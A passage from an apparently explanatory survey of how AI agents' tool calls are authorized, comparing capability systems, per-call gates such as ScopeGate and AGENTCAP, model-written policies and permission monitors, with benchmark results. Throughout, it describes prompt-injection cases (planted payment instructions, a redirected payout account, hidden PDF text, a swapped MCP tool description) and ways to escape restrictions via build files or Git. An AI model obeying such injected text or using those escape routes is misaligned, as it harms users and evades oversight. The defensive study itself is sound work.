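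A model can write a tool in TypeScript, a version of JavaScript with types. The tool runs in a separate process and can reach Agent libOS only through the function `libos.syscall`. For each request, the agent must hold a capability for that operation on that resource, the task's overall limits must allow the request, and it must fit the agent's budget. A fixed policy or a person must also approve it, but approval can't make up for a missing capability. Writing a tool therefore changes what the agent can request but not what it is permitted to do.

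This arrangement uses current conditions, so it can refuse a request if someone has just revoked the capability. Agent libOS also records each external action before attempting it. If the system crashes before a bank replies to a payment request, it marks the outcome as unknown and doesn't automatically resend the payment. But the arrangement can't establish in advance that a function is pure, and it may refuse a request after earlier steps have already taken effect. *ETAS* (2026), a language for agent systems, combines both methods. Its compiler checks which operations a program may request and in what order, and a runtime monitor handles the cases the compiler can't settle.

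To test Agent libOS's checks without involving a model, Zhang ran 33 scripted tasks through it. None of the 119 recorded effects was unauthorised, and there were no wrongful refusals. A wrapper that passed tool calls straight through allowed 20 unauthorised effects out of 29. With confirmation requests added, the wrapper still allowed 20, out of 64. With a real model, all 12 runs were safe and successful, including three in which the agent had to issue a partial refund on a customer website and ignore a planted instruction. Twelve runs with one model are too few to estimate the failure rate.

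Agent libOS has a large trusted computing base, which includes the Python interpreter, the database and the host operating system. An MCP server on the same machine still runs with the user's authority, so Agent libOS is not a full sandbox.

### The costs and the remaining harm

TACIT depends on capture checking, which Scala's documentation calls "still highly experimental and unstable". Safe mode was available only in nightly test versions of the compiler when VirtusLab tried it in 2026. *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* (2026) proposes a further change to let capture sets, which could previously list individual capabilities, also exclude a whole category of them.

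Each service also needs a typed wrapper. TACIT's shared library is about 1,000 lines long, and the airline and retail wrappers are a few hundred lines each, similar in length to the tool descriptions they replaced. Agents can help write the wrappers, but people have to review them, because a function with the wrong type could let the compiler accept code that leaks secrets. Someone also has to decide which data to classify. VirtusLab warns that an agent becomes much less useful if it can't read or change most of the data.

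The compiler's guarantee ends when a program starts another program. Odersky and colleagues recommend allowing only specific safe commands, such as `git diff` and `sbt`, Scala's usual build tool. But `sbt` runs code from the project's build file, so an agent that can edit this file and run `sbt` could escape the restrictions. Git can also start other programs if a project's settings specify them, so Zhang gives agents a fixed set of Git operations and disables many of the features that start other programs.

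A WebAssembly module or another sandbox could contain a program that escapes this way, and the TACIT paper suggests using one. A sandbox alone would not stop the leak that `Classified` prevents, because it might rightly allow an agent both to read a private file and to contact the cloud model. Even with both protections, information could leak through covert channels, such as how long a pure function takes to run.

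Code with the correct types can still do the wrong thing. If an agent may edit a folder, the compiler will accept a program that deletes everything in it. It will also accept a program that uses the wrong supplier's payment capability. Zhao and colleagues suggest more precise types, such as ones that require a number to stay within a certain range. Such a type could cap the payment, but the compiler still could not check which supplier sent the bill.

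## How is each tool call proposed by a model checked before it runs?

Most agents produce tool calls one at a time instead of writing typed programs, so no compiler can reject a bad call. The harness, or the server that offers the tool, has to check each call before it runs. This check can at least use the exact values the model has filled in, such as the account a payment will go to.

### Showing a tool and authorizing a call

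In MCP, a client sends `tools/list` to learn which tools a server offers and `tools/call` to run one with particular arguments. According to Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), a server may list only the tools that the caller's scopes permit. A harness can also leave out tools that a task doesn't need.

Limiting which tools a model can use doesn't determine whether a particular call is acceptable. A model that needs `send_money` to make legitimate payments can also use it to make fraudulent ones. The tool's schema doesn't prevent this, because it only requires the recipient to be text and the amount to be a number, so it accepts an attacker's account number. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* uses "capability gating" for choosing which tools a model can use and "per-call authorization" for deciding whether to allow each call. In these terms, a "capability" is a tool.

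Reviewing a tool before installing it has a similar limit. *PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of an email add-on that includes code, which always calls `send_email(body)`, and written instructions, which tell the model how to compose the body. One version of the instructions uses a fixed template, and another tells the model to copy in a password. The code is identical, so a reviewer who examines only the code has to treat both versions alike. *PACE* proves that such a reviewer can never safely exempt the add-on's emails from later checks. The proof doesn't apply to a reviewer who can tell the versions apart, but the surest evidence is the email itself, which doesn't exist until just before the tool runs.

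### Three frameworks that leave the check to developers

David Mellafe Zuvic, an independent security researcher, audited the public source code of three popular ways to build agents. He found that none of them, by default, checked a call's argument values against fixed rules before running it and refused the call if the check failed.

LangChain and its companion LangGraph look up the tool's name in a table, usually check that the arguments have the right types, and run the tool. Developers can attach functions that observe each call, but their return values don't stop the call. LlamaIndex works in much the same way. If the model names a tool that doesn't exist, LlamaIndex tells the model but doesn't treat this as a security event. The Stripe Agent Toolkit, from the payments company Stripe, lets a developer choose the permitted actions and supply an API key with limited scope. Within those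 limits, it forwards whatever amount, customer and currency the model supplies.

Mellafe Zuvic also connected real LangChain tools to a mock merchant system and gave LangChain a fixed tool call that changed the merchant's payout account to `acct_ATTACKER_999`. LangChain ran it, and a similar test with LlamaIndex had the same result. Both results reflect the frameworks' defaults rather than hidden flaws, since a developer can add the missing check. The audit didn't cover Stripe's own MCP server, which may check more.

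### ScopeGate's five checks

Mellafe Zuvic's proposed remedy, ScopeGate, is ordinary code that runs between the model and the tools. It makes five checks:

1. **Scope:** the tool must be in the operator's policy.
2. **Authorization:** restricted arguments, such as a payout account, must have values on an approved list.
3. **Money:** the amount must be a finite number between zero and a ceiling.
4. **Repetition:** some calls must come with an idempotency key, an identifier that lets a payment service recognize a repeated request and avoid paying twice.
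5. **Default:** ScopeGate refuses any call that hasn't passed all the other checks, including when its own code fails with an error.

The operator has to write the policy without using any model output. If the model could add an account to the approved list, the text that corrupted the tool call could corrupt the list as well.

ScopeGate refused all 48 calls in a fixed set of attempted bypasses, which included misspelled tool names, invisible characters and look-alike letters. While building this set, Mellafe Zuvic found that an early version of ScopeGate let `NaN` ("not a number") through the money check. `Number.isInteger` prevents the same mistake in the JavaScript payment object.

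In a second test, another model, GLM-5.2, tried to get past ScopeGate 40 times and received the reason for each refusal. Of these attempts, 29 were unauthorized calls, all of which ScopeGate refused, nine were malformed, and two were harmless. A more skilled attacker or one with more time might do better, but ScopeGate's rules are simple enough that the result is believable.

The paper's attack success rates count attempted calls, which ran in a sandbox and harmed nobody. When the injected text presented the unauthorized call as part of the user's task, 12 inexpensive models attempted it in 60.3% of trials on average, and 15 flagship models in 18.9%. ScopeGate doesn't lower these rates, but it can block the calls that models attempt. In a simulated payment assistant, two of the inexpensive models attempted the attacker's payout in all ten trials, and ScopeGate stopped it every time.

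ScopeGate's approved list doesn't depend on what the user has asked for. If it includes 30 suppliers, an injected instruction can still make the assistant pay any of them, up to the ceiling.

### How AGENTCAP authorizes a payment

*AGENTCAP* (Suresh and Gao, 2026) uses the user's request as evidence when deciding whether to allow a call. A wrapper replaces the agent's MCP tools and receives each call the model proposes. The wrapper sends the call to a policy engine, which compares it with rules written by the developer and issues a signed token if the call passes. A gateway then verifies the token and forwards the call to the real MCP server. The design relies on the agent having no other route to the tools.

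The token has thirteen fields:

| Fields | Example for a payment |
|---|---|
| Token identifier, agent, session | Token 52, invoice assistant, this morning's session |
| Action, resource | Write, `bank_account/transfers` |
| Declared intent | `pay_bill` |
| Time of issue, expiry | 30 seconds apart |
| Call budget | 1 |
| Agent's trust score when issued | 0.8 |
| Prerequisites, groups for forbidden combinations | A balance check, `financial_write` |
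| Reference to the audit record | The log entry for this decision |

When the model proposes a call, it includes an intent chosen from a fixed list. The agent also has a trust score between 0 and 1 that reflects its recent behavior.

Suppose the owner types "pay 400 euros to account 7731". The assistant checks the balance and reads some past transactions. An attacker has made a tiny transfer to the business, with a description that tells the assistant to pay account 9090. Under the banking policy, the policy engine applies seven conditions in this order:

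| Condition | Payment to 7731 | Payment to 9090 |
|---|---|---|
| The system has not isolated the agent for bad conduct | Passes | Passes |
| The tool is in the policy's catalog | Passes | Passes |
| Protected arguments have trusted support | Passes: the owner typed 7731 | Fails: 9090 appears only in a transaction description |
| The policy allows the declared intent | Passes | Would pass |
| The trust score is at least 0.8 | Passes | Would pass |
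| The agent holds a valid token for checking the balance | Passes | Would pass |
| The new token would not complete a forbidden combination | Passes | Would pass |

For the legitimate payment, the engine issues a token that allows one call within 30 seconds. The gateway checks the token's signature, expiry, remaining budget, agent, action and resource, and whether anyone has revoked it. The gateway then forwards the payment, which uses up the budget. For the injected payment, the engine issues no token, logs the refusal and gives the model the reason, so the model can return to the owner's task.

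Only the third condition distinguishes the two payments. The declared intent can't distinguish them, because a model following the attacker's instruction can also declare `pay_bill`. Suresh and Gao acknowledge that the declaration isn't trustworthy. It is meant to stop the agent from using a token for a purpose other than the one it was issued for.

The third condition depends on argument provenance, a record of where each value came from. Whoever writes the policy marks which arguments need protection and which sources are trusted. The user's request and certain fields in the application's data might be trusted, for example, and the text of emails untrusted. The engine rejects a protected argument if its value comes only from untrusted sources. A value that appears in both kinds of source is acceptable, so an attacker can't block a payment to 7731 just by mentioning that number in an email.

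The published banking policy restricts the recipient of a payment but not the amount, so an instruction to pay account 7731 ten times what the owner intended would pass all seven conditions. The engine will also refuse a legitimate payment if the owner tells the invoice assistant only to "pay the paper supplier" and the account number is in the invoice. The policy's author can prevent this by marking that part of the invoice as trusted, but the engine would then also accept a false account number there.

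*ToolFence* (Li, Cao and Xiao, 2026) offers a partial solution. It can require a payment's recipient to come from a particular source, such as the bill the user named. It would then allow a payment to the account in that bill and refuse one to an account in an unrelated message, even if the tool and the amount were the same. This check would not stop a payment to an attacker who wrote the bill.

AGENTCAP's trust score might let an attacker who can't steal money stop a business from paying its bills. Each normal outcome raises the score t to t + 0.01(1 − t), and each refusal or other anomaly lowers it to 0.7t. From the default start of 0.8, three anomalies take it to 0.56, 0.39 and 0.27. The agent loses write access after the second and all access after the third. But the banking policy requires a score of 0.8 for payments, so with the default settings a single refusal would block every later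 payment until the agent had nearly 80 normal outcomes.

### Passing a token to a helper

An agent can delegate part of its authority to a helper agent in the same session. If the original token covers action a on resource r, with call budget b, expiry time e and remaining delegation depth d, the helper's token must satisfy

a′ = a, r′ = r, b′ ≤ b, e′ ≤ e, d′ < d.

Suppose a supervisor may read transactions five times before 10:05, with a remaining delegation depth of 2. It can sign a new token that lets a worker read them twice before 10:02, with a depth of 1, if the policy allows supervisors to delegate to workers. Because the depth falls with each delegation, the chain has to end. Each time the worker uses the token, the gateway checks every signature, limit and revocation in the chain.

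This rule is stricter than it may look, and less useful, because it requires the same resource. A supervisor with a token for `bank_account/transfers` can't narrow it to transfers to a single supplier, though the holder of a macaroon could do so by adding a condition. The token also has no field for the recipient. That doesn't matter when the wrapper submits exactly the call that the policy engine examined, but if a supervisor delegated a payment token, something else would have to check the recipient the worker chose.

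### What AGENTCAP's tests found

Suresh and Gao tested AGENTCAP on all of AgentDojo, with 97 ordinary tasks and 949 attacked ones. They also used InjecAgent, a benchmark with 1,054 attacks that try to cause harm directly or steal data. Each attack ran with and without AGENTCAP on two OpenAI models:

| Benchmark and model | Attack success: without → with | User's task completed under attack: without → with |
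|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo, GPT-4o | 45.63% → 5.09% | 73.61% → 74.88% |
| AgentDojo, GPT-5.4 | 33.23% → 0.00% | 75.68% → 75.04% |
| InjecAgent, GPT-4o | 23.24% → 8.63% | 74.10% → 69.92% |
| InjecAgent, GPT-5.4 | 11.95% → 0.00% | 72.96% → 69.92% |

Unlike ScopeGate's figures, these count attacks in which the attacker's action took place. AGENTCAP also reduced task completion when there was no attack. On AgentDojo's ordinary tasks, it fell by 3.1 percentage points with GPT-4o and 7.2 with GPT-5.4, or three and seven tasks out of 97. On 51 ordinary tasks that Suresh and Gao derived from InjecAgent, it fell by 3.9 and 2.0 points, or two tasks and one.

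Some of the attacks that still worked on GPT-4o aimed only to change the text of the agent's answer, which a check on tool calls can't prevent. In the others, the gateway enforced the policy correctly, but either the policy didn't protect the argument the attacker chose, or its author hadn't marked the field containing the false value as untrusted.

With GPT-4o on AgentDojo, AGENTCAP matched the attack success rate of Progent, an earlier system in which a model writes a policy for each task. AGENTCAP completed 78.35% of ordinary tasks, compared with 68.04% for Progent. Under attack, AGENTCAP completed 74.88% and Progent 59.64%. Progent's policies often allowed only the argument values the model had predicted, so they blocked legitimate calls with other values. However, Suresh and Gao wrote AGENTCAP's policies by hand after reading descriptions of the benchmark's tasks. They finalized the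 policies before the tests and included no rules against particular attacks, but some of AGENTCAP's advantage may still come from having policies written by people who knew the tasks.

It is also easy to make mistakes when writing these policies. AGENTCAP includes a program that checks a policy for contradictions. In a customer-service example, it found that an agent could never get permission to use `delete_customer`, because one rule required the agent to hold another token first and a second rule forbade holding both. Suresh and Gao had to correct a similar mistake in the banking policy.

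The checks add almost no delay compared with the seconds a model usually takes to produce its next call. The median time was 67 microseconds to issue a token and 80 to verify it, and a chain of three delegations took 151.

Each result comes from a single run, so differences of a point or two may be chance. The attacks were also fixed in advance, whereas an attacker who knew about AGENTCAP would look for unprotected arguments and mislabeled fields. The GPT-4o results show that some existed. The zeros for GPT-5.4 are encouraging, but they don't rule out a successful attack.

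### Evidence from similar systems

PACE makes a similar check on each call and also traces whether untrusted or secret data could have influenced it. Li, Wang and colleagues gave an attacker up to 50 attempts at each of 30 forbidden actions from AgentDojo and let it adapt to PACE's responses. The attacker succeeded at 21 of the actions against an undefended agent and none against PACE. With only 30 cases, the true success rate against PACE could still be as high as about 11%.

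Switching PACE's parts on and off in 1,167 test cases showed what each contributed. The authority check alone stopped every AgentDojo attack in this set, but it reduced completed tasks from 76.8% to 64.6%. On MCPTox, a benchmark of poisoned tool descriptions, it raised refusals from 42.2% to 99.3%. Adding a part that adapts calls at the point of execution lowered refusals to 1.6%. On full benchmarks, the complete system reduced usefulness by at most three percentage points. In the 1,167-case set, however, it cut the completion rate on AgentDyn from 66.7% to 33.3%. AgentDyn's tasks require the agent to change its plans and follow legitimate instructions from other people, which a strict check can easily misclassify as an attack.

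ToolFence sends calls that its rules don't cover to a separate model for review. On AgentDojo with the model Qwen3-max, it cut attack success from 21.2% to zero and reduced usefulness by 2.0 points. The review helps with steps that nobody foresaw, but it also once again lets a model expand what the agent may do.

### Are these tokens capabilities?

Suresh and Gao call their tokens capabilities. Like capabilities, the tokens are unforgeable, carry a right to act, and let an agent pass on a weaker version. But a capability must also designate the resource, and AGENTCAP's payment token designates only `bank_account/transfers`, which covers every possible payment. The model can choose any recipient by writing an account number, and the policy engine then checks whether a rule permits the call. In Miller's terms, this is designation without authority, the arrangement that let Tymshare's customer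 overwrite the billing file.

AGENTCAP is therefore closer to a very detailed access list that issues a signed ticket for each decision. Its provenance check supplies some of the information that an ordinary access list lacks, but its protection depends on the policy's author thinking of every argument that matters. Other agent systems use the word "capability" still more loosely. In ToolFence, a capability is a rule about a tool, its effects, its arguments and a budget. According to Li, Cao and Xiao, CaMeL uses the word for labels that record where data came from and who may read it.

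A harness could follow the strict definition by offering the model a tool called `pay_paper_supplier`, whose only argument is the amount. The tool would use a payment object with a fixed payee and limit, so the model could not pass it an attacker's account number. In this design, the harness authorizes actions mostly by choosing which tools to show the model. MCP allows a server to offer such tools, but the list may depend only on the credentials in the request, not on earlier requests in the same connection. The harness would therefore need a separate token for each task. It would also have to know the supplier before the model started work, and a model with several such tools could still choose the wrong one.

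Code outside the model has to check any token that authorizes a tool call. *Instruction Self-Arbitration Is Not a Trust Boundary* (2026) describes a design that puts a signed, expiring token in the model's instructions and tells the model that dangerous calls require it. The model can ignore this instruction, so the token is only advisory unless the program that runs the tools also requires it. In a later version, each token was valid for one use, and the program rejected all 452 attempts to reuse one.

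### What products do by default

LangChain leaves developers to decide which tool calls need approval. Its *Human in the loop* explains how to add a component that pauses chosen tools until a person approves, edits or rejects the call. Tools that the developer doesn't list run without approval, according to a copy of the code in Supermodel Tools' *HumanInTheLoopMiddleware*. Developers can also supply a function that checks a call's arguments to determine whether to pause. LangChain runs this function again after the person answers, and if the result is now that no pause is needed, the tool runs even if the person rejected the call. By contrast, the approval component in Strands Agents, another framework, requires approval by default for every tool that the developer hasn't exempted, according to *strands.vended_interventions.hitl*.

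Claude Code used to ask the user before every file change and shell command (Anthropic, *Auto mode for Claude Code*). Users approved 97% of these requests, many probably without much thought. Since 14 August 2026, new sessions on Anthropic's individual paid plans and its Team plan have defaulted to "auto mode" (Anthropic, *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*, 2026). In auto mode, a second model, called a classifier, reviews each call and blocks those that look destructive, irreversible or aimed at outside systems. After three blocks in a row or twenty in a session, Claude Code goes back to asking the user. In October, Anthropic announced that most of its other Claude apps would also switch to auto mode.

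Anthropic compared human approval with a classifier by paying 1,053 testers to do coding work and replacing one approval request in each session with a dangerous command. The testers rejected 13.6% of these commands, and the classifier blocked 89%. The testers' rejection rate fell as sessions went on, to about 5% after 50 requests. They may have been less careful than usual because they weren't working on their own code, but the gap between them and the classifier is too wide for that to fully explain it.

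The classifier still allowed about one in nine of the dangerous commands. In a separate test by the safety company Apollo Research, it missed 7% of attacks designed to get past it, down from 12% before Anthropic made improvements. Anthropic also reports that none of 720 prompt injection attempts worked in auto mode, but this is weak evidence about the classifier because only 0.09% worked on Anthropic's latest models without the classifier. A classifier can judge a command that no policy author has thought of, but it can't guarantee a limit the way ScopeGate's ceiling does. Anthropic still recommends that people review important changes to live systems themselves.

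Microsoft's Foundry, a platform for building agents, screens the input and output of every tool, according to a Microsoft post from July 2026. Microsoft also describes a service that developers can build for their agents to consult before each call. The service can allow the call, deny it, require approval or mask some of the data.

### What official guidance recommends

In the Australian Signals Directorate's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (May 2026), cyber security agencies from Australia, the United States, Canada, New Zealand and the United Kingdom warn against checking an agent's permissions only when it starts. In their example, an attacker takes over a scheduling component in a customer-support system. The agent still relies on its earlier authorization, so the attacker can use account functions that should have required a new check for each request. The agencies also advise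 organizations to use agents only for low-risk tasks that don't involve sensitive data, which would rule out the invoice assistant.

*Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2026), published separately that month by the US National Security Agency, recommends checking the arguments of every tool call against the expected format, range and context. It also warns that an MCP server can often change its behavior after a user approves it, without asking again. In one demonstration, a malicious server showed a harmless tool description at installation and later replaced it with one that made the agent expose WhatsApp messages.

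The MCP specification is less strict. It requires servers to validate inputs and control access, but only recommends that a person be able to refuse tool calls. It also recommends that clients show users a tool's inputs before sending them, which would at least let the owner see the account number.

Microsoft's *Least privilege for AI agents* (2026) advises that the services behind the tools should check the agent's role and scope on every call, instead of relying on the harness to do it. This protects a bank from a faulty harness. But while the bank can confirm that the assistant may make payments, it cannot tell whether the account number came from the owner or from a stranger's email.

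## How does a system work out how much authority a task needs?

Somebody has to set the limits that a check on a tool call enforces. An agent's developer can't set them all in advance, because the user gives the task in a sentence, such as "comment on GitLab issue 745 that we're done", an example from Christodorescu and colleagues. The system has to work out from those words that the agent may open that issue and write in its comment box, and may do nothing else in GitLab. If the user then asks for a summary of the issue, the limits have to change. The system can either erase the agent's context and start again, which is safe but loses useful information, or set new limits while the context already contains text written by strangers.

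Models sometimes misjudge how much access they need. In one case Anthropic describes, someone asked Claude to set up read-only access to billing data, and Claude chose a cloud role with full administrative control. Claude Code's classifier blocked the choice. But limits that are too narrow block legitimate work, and users may then switch them off. Surapani and colleagues therefore want researchers to measure wrongful refusals and the burden on users as well as the attacks a system prevents.

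### The user's choice as the grant

The oldest method is to use a powerbox, which avoids the need to guess. A powerbox is a trusted program that can reach all the user's files and shows a dialog that the requesting program can't control. The word processor's "Open" dialog, described at the start, is an example.

CapDesk, the virus-resistant desktop written in E, gave each application a powerbox. Polaris, developed at Hewlett-Packard's research labs in the 2000s, applied the idea to ordinary Windows XP programs. It ran each protected program under a separate account with few permissions. When the user opened a file, Polaris copied it to where that account could reach it, and later copied any changes back. A virus in a spreadsheet could ruin that spreadsheet but not the user's other documents. Today, macOS uses a powerbox for sandboxed applications.

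A powerbox relies on clicks that the user would make anyway, but an agent is meant to remove those clicks. The owner of the invoice assistant doesn't want to pick out each message. A harness could still let the owner choose the mail folder and the supplier from a menu, and turn those choices into capabilities before the model reads anything. This wouldn't work for resources that nobody knows about yet, such as a second GitLab issue that the first one depends on.

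### What people do with approval prompts

Many agents ask the user for approval instead. An approval prompt can look like a powerbox, except that the agent chooses the action and the user only confirms it. A user who carelessly approves a command may never find out what it did, whereas one who opens the wrong file through a powerbox will probably notice.

The testers who missed most of the dangerous commands in Anthropic's experiment were not working on their own code, but real users' settings suggest that they also give commands little scrutiny. By June 2026, about half the active users of Claude Code's command-line version had written a rule that let some shell commands run without a prompt. Many of these rules allowed any Python or JavaScript program, which in practice allows almost anything. A quarter of interactive sessions started with permission prompts switched off. Users rejected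 39% of the plans Claude presented but only 3% of individual permission requests. People may read more carefully when asked about what they want done, but the plans may also have contained more mistakes.

*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examines 290 incident reports and finds that user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 of those, the user had let the agent approve its own actions, and in 31, the prompt didn't make clear what the command would do to the user's files. For example, `python3 setup.py` looks routine but runs whatever code is in the script.

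Software practitioners interviewed and surveyed for *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) said they had given up reviewing such information because of time pressure, fatigue or information overload. The paper warns that repeated approvals may reflect habit rather than trust, so a system that learned its limits from past approvals could learn the wrong ones. Participants also saw agents do more than asked without crossing any permission boundary. A sandbox needs fewer approval prompts, but Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* calls it "high-maintenance" because someone has to configure it for each new thing the agent needs to do.

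### Policies written by a model

Several systems try to reduce the number of prompts by deriving limits from the user's request. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) has a language model write a policy that lists the permitted tools and argument values. In one example, a user asks an agent to carry out the tasks in an email from Alice. The first policy allows only a search for that email. In it, Alice asks for a summary of recent emails to be posted to the user's account on Slack, a workplace chat service, so the policy has to expand to allow reading mail and posting to Slack. Once the agent has looked up the user's Slack name, the policy narrows to allow posting only to that name. One of the recent emails then turns out to contain an instruction to forward the whole inbox to a stranger.

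The model that writes the first policy sees only the user's request and the list of tools, so text in an email can't influence it. Updates are riskier because they depend on information in the tool results. Progent first asks a model whether the latest tool call could justify an update, without showing it the result. If so, a model reads the result and proposes a new policy. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) objected to an earlier version of Progent because hostile text could loosen the policy at this point.

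The current version compares the old and new policies with an SMT solver, a program that determines whether logical conditions can all be true together. Let A(P) be the set of tool calls that policy P allows. The new policy P′ takes effect automatically if

A(P′) ⊆ A(P).

Otherwise the update is an expansion and needs an approver's consent. Adding a tool to forward the inbox is an expansion, however persuasive the attacker's email is, but so was adding the Slack tool. The solver can't determine which of the two the user would want, so it flags both and leaves the decision to the approver.

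With GPT-4o on AgentDojo, 39.9% of attacks succeeded without Progent and 1.0% with it. On ASB, another benchmark, the rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. The approver in these tests accepted every expansion, so the low rates reflect how well the model wrote policies, not the solver's guarantee. Without policy updates, the AgentDojo rate was 2.5%. It fell to zero when a person reviewed every expansion, but Shi and colleagues assumed a careful reviewer who would never allow payments to arbitrary recipients. Only 6% of updates were expansions, so the reviewer would have had few decisions to make. They also excluded two attacks that persuade the agent to choose a different hotel, because these require no extra authority. They report little loss of usefulness, although Suresh and Gao measured a larger loss when comparing Progent with AGENTCAP.

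ToolFence, from Li and colleagues, further restricts what the policy's writer can read. The model that turns the request into rules receives only the request and tool schemas that the operator controls, not tool results or the tool descriptions that outside servers supply. Its rules can tie an argument to a particular source, require an exact value from the request, or leave the agent free to choose. A second model reviews calls outside these rules and can add a missing step.

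Li and colleagues switched these parts off one at a time, using Llama 3.3 70B and ASB's attacks:

| Configuration | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks completed under attack |
|---|---|---|
| No defense | 45.4% | 40.1% |
| Full ToolFence | 5.1% | 44.3% |
| Without the argument rules | 24.0% | 45.0% |
| Without the second model | 4.8% | 35.8% |

The argument rules provide most of the security. The policy in the last row can't be expanded, and it blocked so much legitimate work that the agent completed fewer tasks than it did with no defense.

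The second model can also grant too much authority. AgentLAB is a benchmark whose attacks spread their instructions over several records, so that a harmful action looks like a necessary step. With Qwen3-max, 29.4% of these attacks still succeeded against ToolFence, down from 76.3%. In a separate test of 285 unauthorized calls, ToolFence accepted five. All five came from one task in which the user's request gave the attacker's account as that of a new landlord, so a system that trusts the request can't catch them.

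### Calculating the smallest set of permissions

*MiniScope* (Zhu, Tseng and colleagues, 2025) calculates which permissions a task needs. It starts from the OAuth scopes that services already publish, each of which permits certain tool calls. It treats scopes that permit more calls as broader and therefore more sensitive. The agent submits a plan, and MiniScope uses integer programming, a method for finding the best combination of whole-number choices, to select the least permissive set of scopes that covers it. MiniScope asks the user to approve any new scopes, much as a phone does for apps, and then checks each call against what the user has granted.

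Zhu and colleagues tested this on model-generated requests for ten real applications, including Gmail, Slack and Dropbox. When they had language models choose the permissions instead, commercial models found the best set 70–83% of the time and open models 20–34%. MiniScope's solver also found six real connectors between AI assistants and other services that had more permissions than they needed. It added at most 7% to running time. In a simulation of three months of Gmail use, the confirmation rate ranged from 18% to 60%, depending on the type of user. Sixty percent is high, given how people respond to prompts.

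MiniScope calculates the least authority that the agent's plan needs, which may differ from what the user's task needs. If an agent has read a malicious email, it can submit a plan that includes sending mail. MiniScope will correctly calculate that the plan needs permission to send, and only the user can then object. MiniScope also doesn't try to stop extra calls within an approved scope.

There may not be a single smallest set of permissions. *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* (2026) notes that Zhu and colleagues don't discuss whether their solution is unique. Suppose an agent needs to read and label messages. One scope allows reading, labeling and deleting, while another allows reading, labeling and sending. Neither contains the other, and both permit three operations, so counting operations can't determine which is better. That depends on whether the user is more worried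 about losing mail or leaking it.

The three systems therefore fail in different ways:

| | Progent | ToolFence | MiniScope |
|---|---|---|---|
| Who sets the limits | A language model | A language model, with a second one for missing steps | A solver, from the agent's plan |
| What can influence them | The request at first, then tool results | The request and operator-controlled schemas, then the agent's proposed steps | Anything the agent read before it planned |
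| If they are too wide | An attack within the policy succeeds | An attack that satisfies the rules succeeds | The user has to notice at the prompt |
| If they are too narrow | The approver has to accept an expansion | The second model has to add the step | The user gets another prompt |

### One source for each field

Zheng, Zhang and Mao (2026), in *LLM Agent Capabilities Should Follow Task Intent and Context Source*, argue that no single source contains everything needed to define a grant. Their prototype, INTENTCAP, builds each grant from four sources:

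| Source | What it may supply |
|---|---|
| The user's intent | The goal, the selected files, the permitted destinations and any approvals |
| Workflow instructions | The steps of the procedure |
| Tool schemas | The form of the call and the credentials it uses |
| The runtime environment | Observed values, such as text from a file |

In one design, a grant is called a lease and consists of fields such as the tool's name, the destination and the approval scope. Each field belongs to one source, and only that source can fill it.

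In their main example, a user selects two PDFs and asks an agent to extract the tables, save them as spreadsheets and create one issue in the GitHub repository `org/proj`. INTENTCAP handles the issue as follows:

1. It labels each input by where it came from. The user's message counts as intent, and text from the PDFs counts as runtime environment.
2. Ordinary code reads the limits of the user's authority from structured parts of the message, such as the selected files and the named repository.
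3. A language model proposes a lease for the tool `create_issue`. The repository field contains `org/proj`, with a pointer to the place in the user's message where that name appears. The body of the issue may contain text from the PDFs. The lease allows one issue and expires after its first use.
4. A checker made of ordinary code confirms that each field comes from the right source and that the lease doesn't exceed the user's authority. Only then does the call go ahead.

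If hidden text in a PDF contains an instruction to create the issue in `attacker/repo`, the model may follow it and propose a lease for that repository. The checker refuses the lease because the repository's name isn't in the user's message. The same rule blocks the lease if the agent mistakes a table heading for the repository's name.

Leases can only narrow the user's authority. The model may choose one of several permitted destinations or request a smaller budget, but it can't add a destination or extend an approval. If the agent passes part of the task to a helper, the helper's lease has to be narrower than the agent's.

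INTENTCAP is similar to a powerbox because its authority comes from things the user has selected. It also has a powerbox's difficulty with unknown resources. For example, it would refuse a payment if the account number appeared only in an invoice. It also gives no authority to a document that the user pastes into the request, because it can't verify who wrote it.

Zheng and colleagues tested the checker by replaying events from AgentDojo, MCPTox, InjecAgent and τ²-bench. It accepted no unsafe action in 3,746 security-related events, and INTENTCAP covered all 3,813 harmless actions in a test based on τ²-bench. When they merged the four sources into one trusted context, the checker wrongly accepted 3,593 (94%) of the 3,823 events it should have refused. Merging two sources at a time produced error rates between 43% and 50%.

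These figures show that the checker depends on keeping the sources apart. They are less useful for comparing INTENTCAP with other defenses, because merging the sources removes the information the checker uses. Zheng and colleagues have not yet tested end-to-end attacks, in which an attacker tries to make a working agent cause harm, or attackers who adapt to the labeling. They also haven't measured the delay the checks add.

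### When a grant should end

The authority an agent needs for one step may be excessive for the next. *CreepScope* (2026) therefore distinguishes authorizing each call from keeping authority small throughout a task. *Lingering Authority* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) studies what happens when a coding agent keeps access it no longer needs.

In one example, an agent has to add a timeout setting to `src/api.py` and carry it through to `src/serialization.py`. It starts with access to the first file and its tests. When it asks for the second file, a monitor called PORTICO checks the request against a contract written before the task began. The contract allows it, so PORTICO gives the agent temporary handles for reading and changing the file. When the tests pass, PORTICO removes the handles from the options the model sees and blocks any further use of them. PORTICO relies on trusted events to end a grant,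 such as a test it ran itself or a person's decision. The model can't extend or end a grant by claiming that it still needs the file or has finished.

Santos-Grueiro compared PORTICO with a version that made the same grants at the same moments but never withdrew them. Both completed the task in all ten runs. When the agent later tried to reread a file, PORTICO always refused and the other version always allowed it. PORTICO also blocked all six forbidden writes attempted through old handles, while the other version carried them out. These results follow almost directly from the two designs. They confirm that revocation works but don't measure how often an agent would misuse leftover access in practice.

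The costs are more informative. Santos-Grueiro ran 37 coding tasks five times each, many of which needed files outside the starting set:

| Arrangement | Tasks completed | Runs that stayed within the task's limits |
|---|---|---|
| Fixed list of permitted tools and paths | 97% | 92% |
| PORTICO with only the starting permissions | 21% | 100% |
| PORTICO with temporary grants | 87% | 100% |

With temporary grants, agents completed most of the work that the narrow starting permissions had blocked. On 42 further combinations of models and tasks from real software projects, PORTICO completed 31, while a version that never revoked access completed all 42. Some contracts ended a grant too early or provided no way to renew it, and some models didn't request a new one. Whoever writes the contract therefore has to predict which resources the agent will need and when it will have finished with each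 one. Santos-Grueiro didn't measure how long this takes.

### Showing risky tools only when a step needs them

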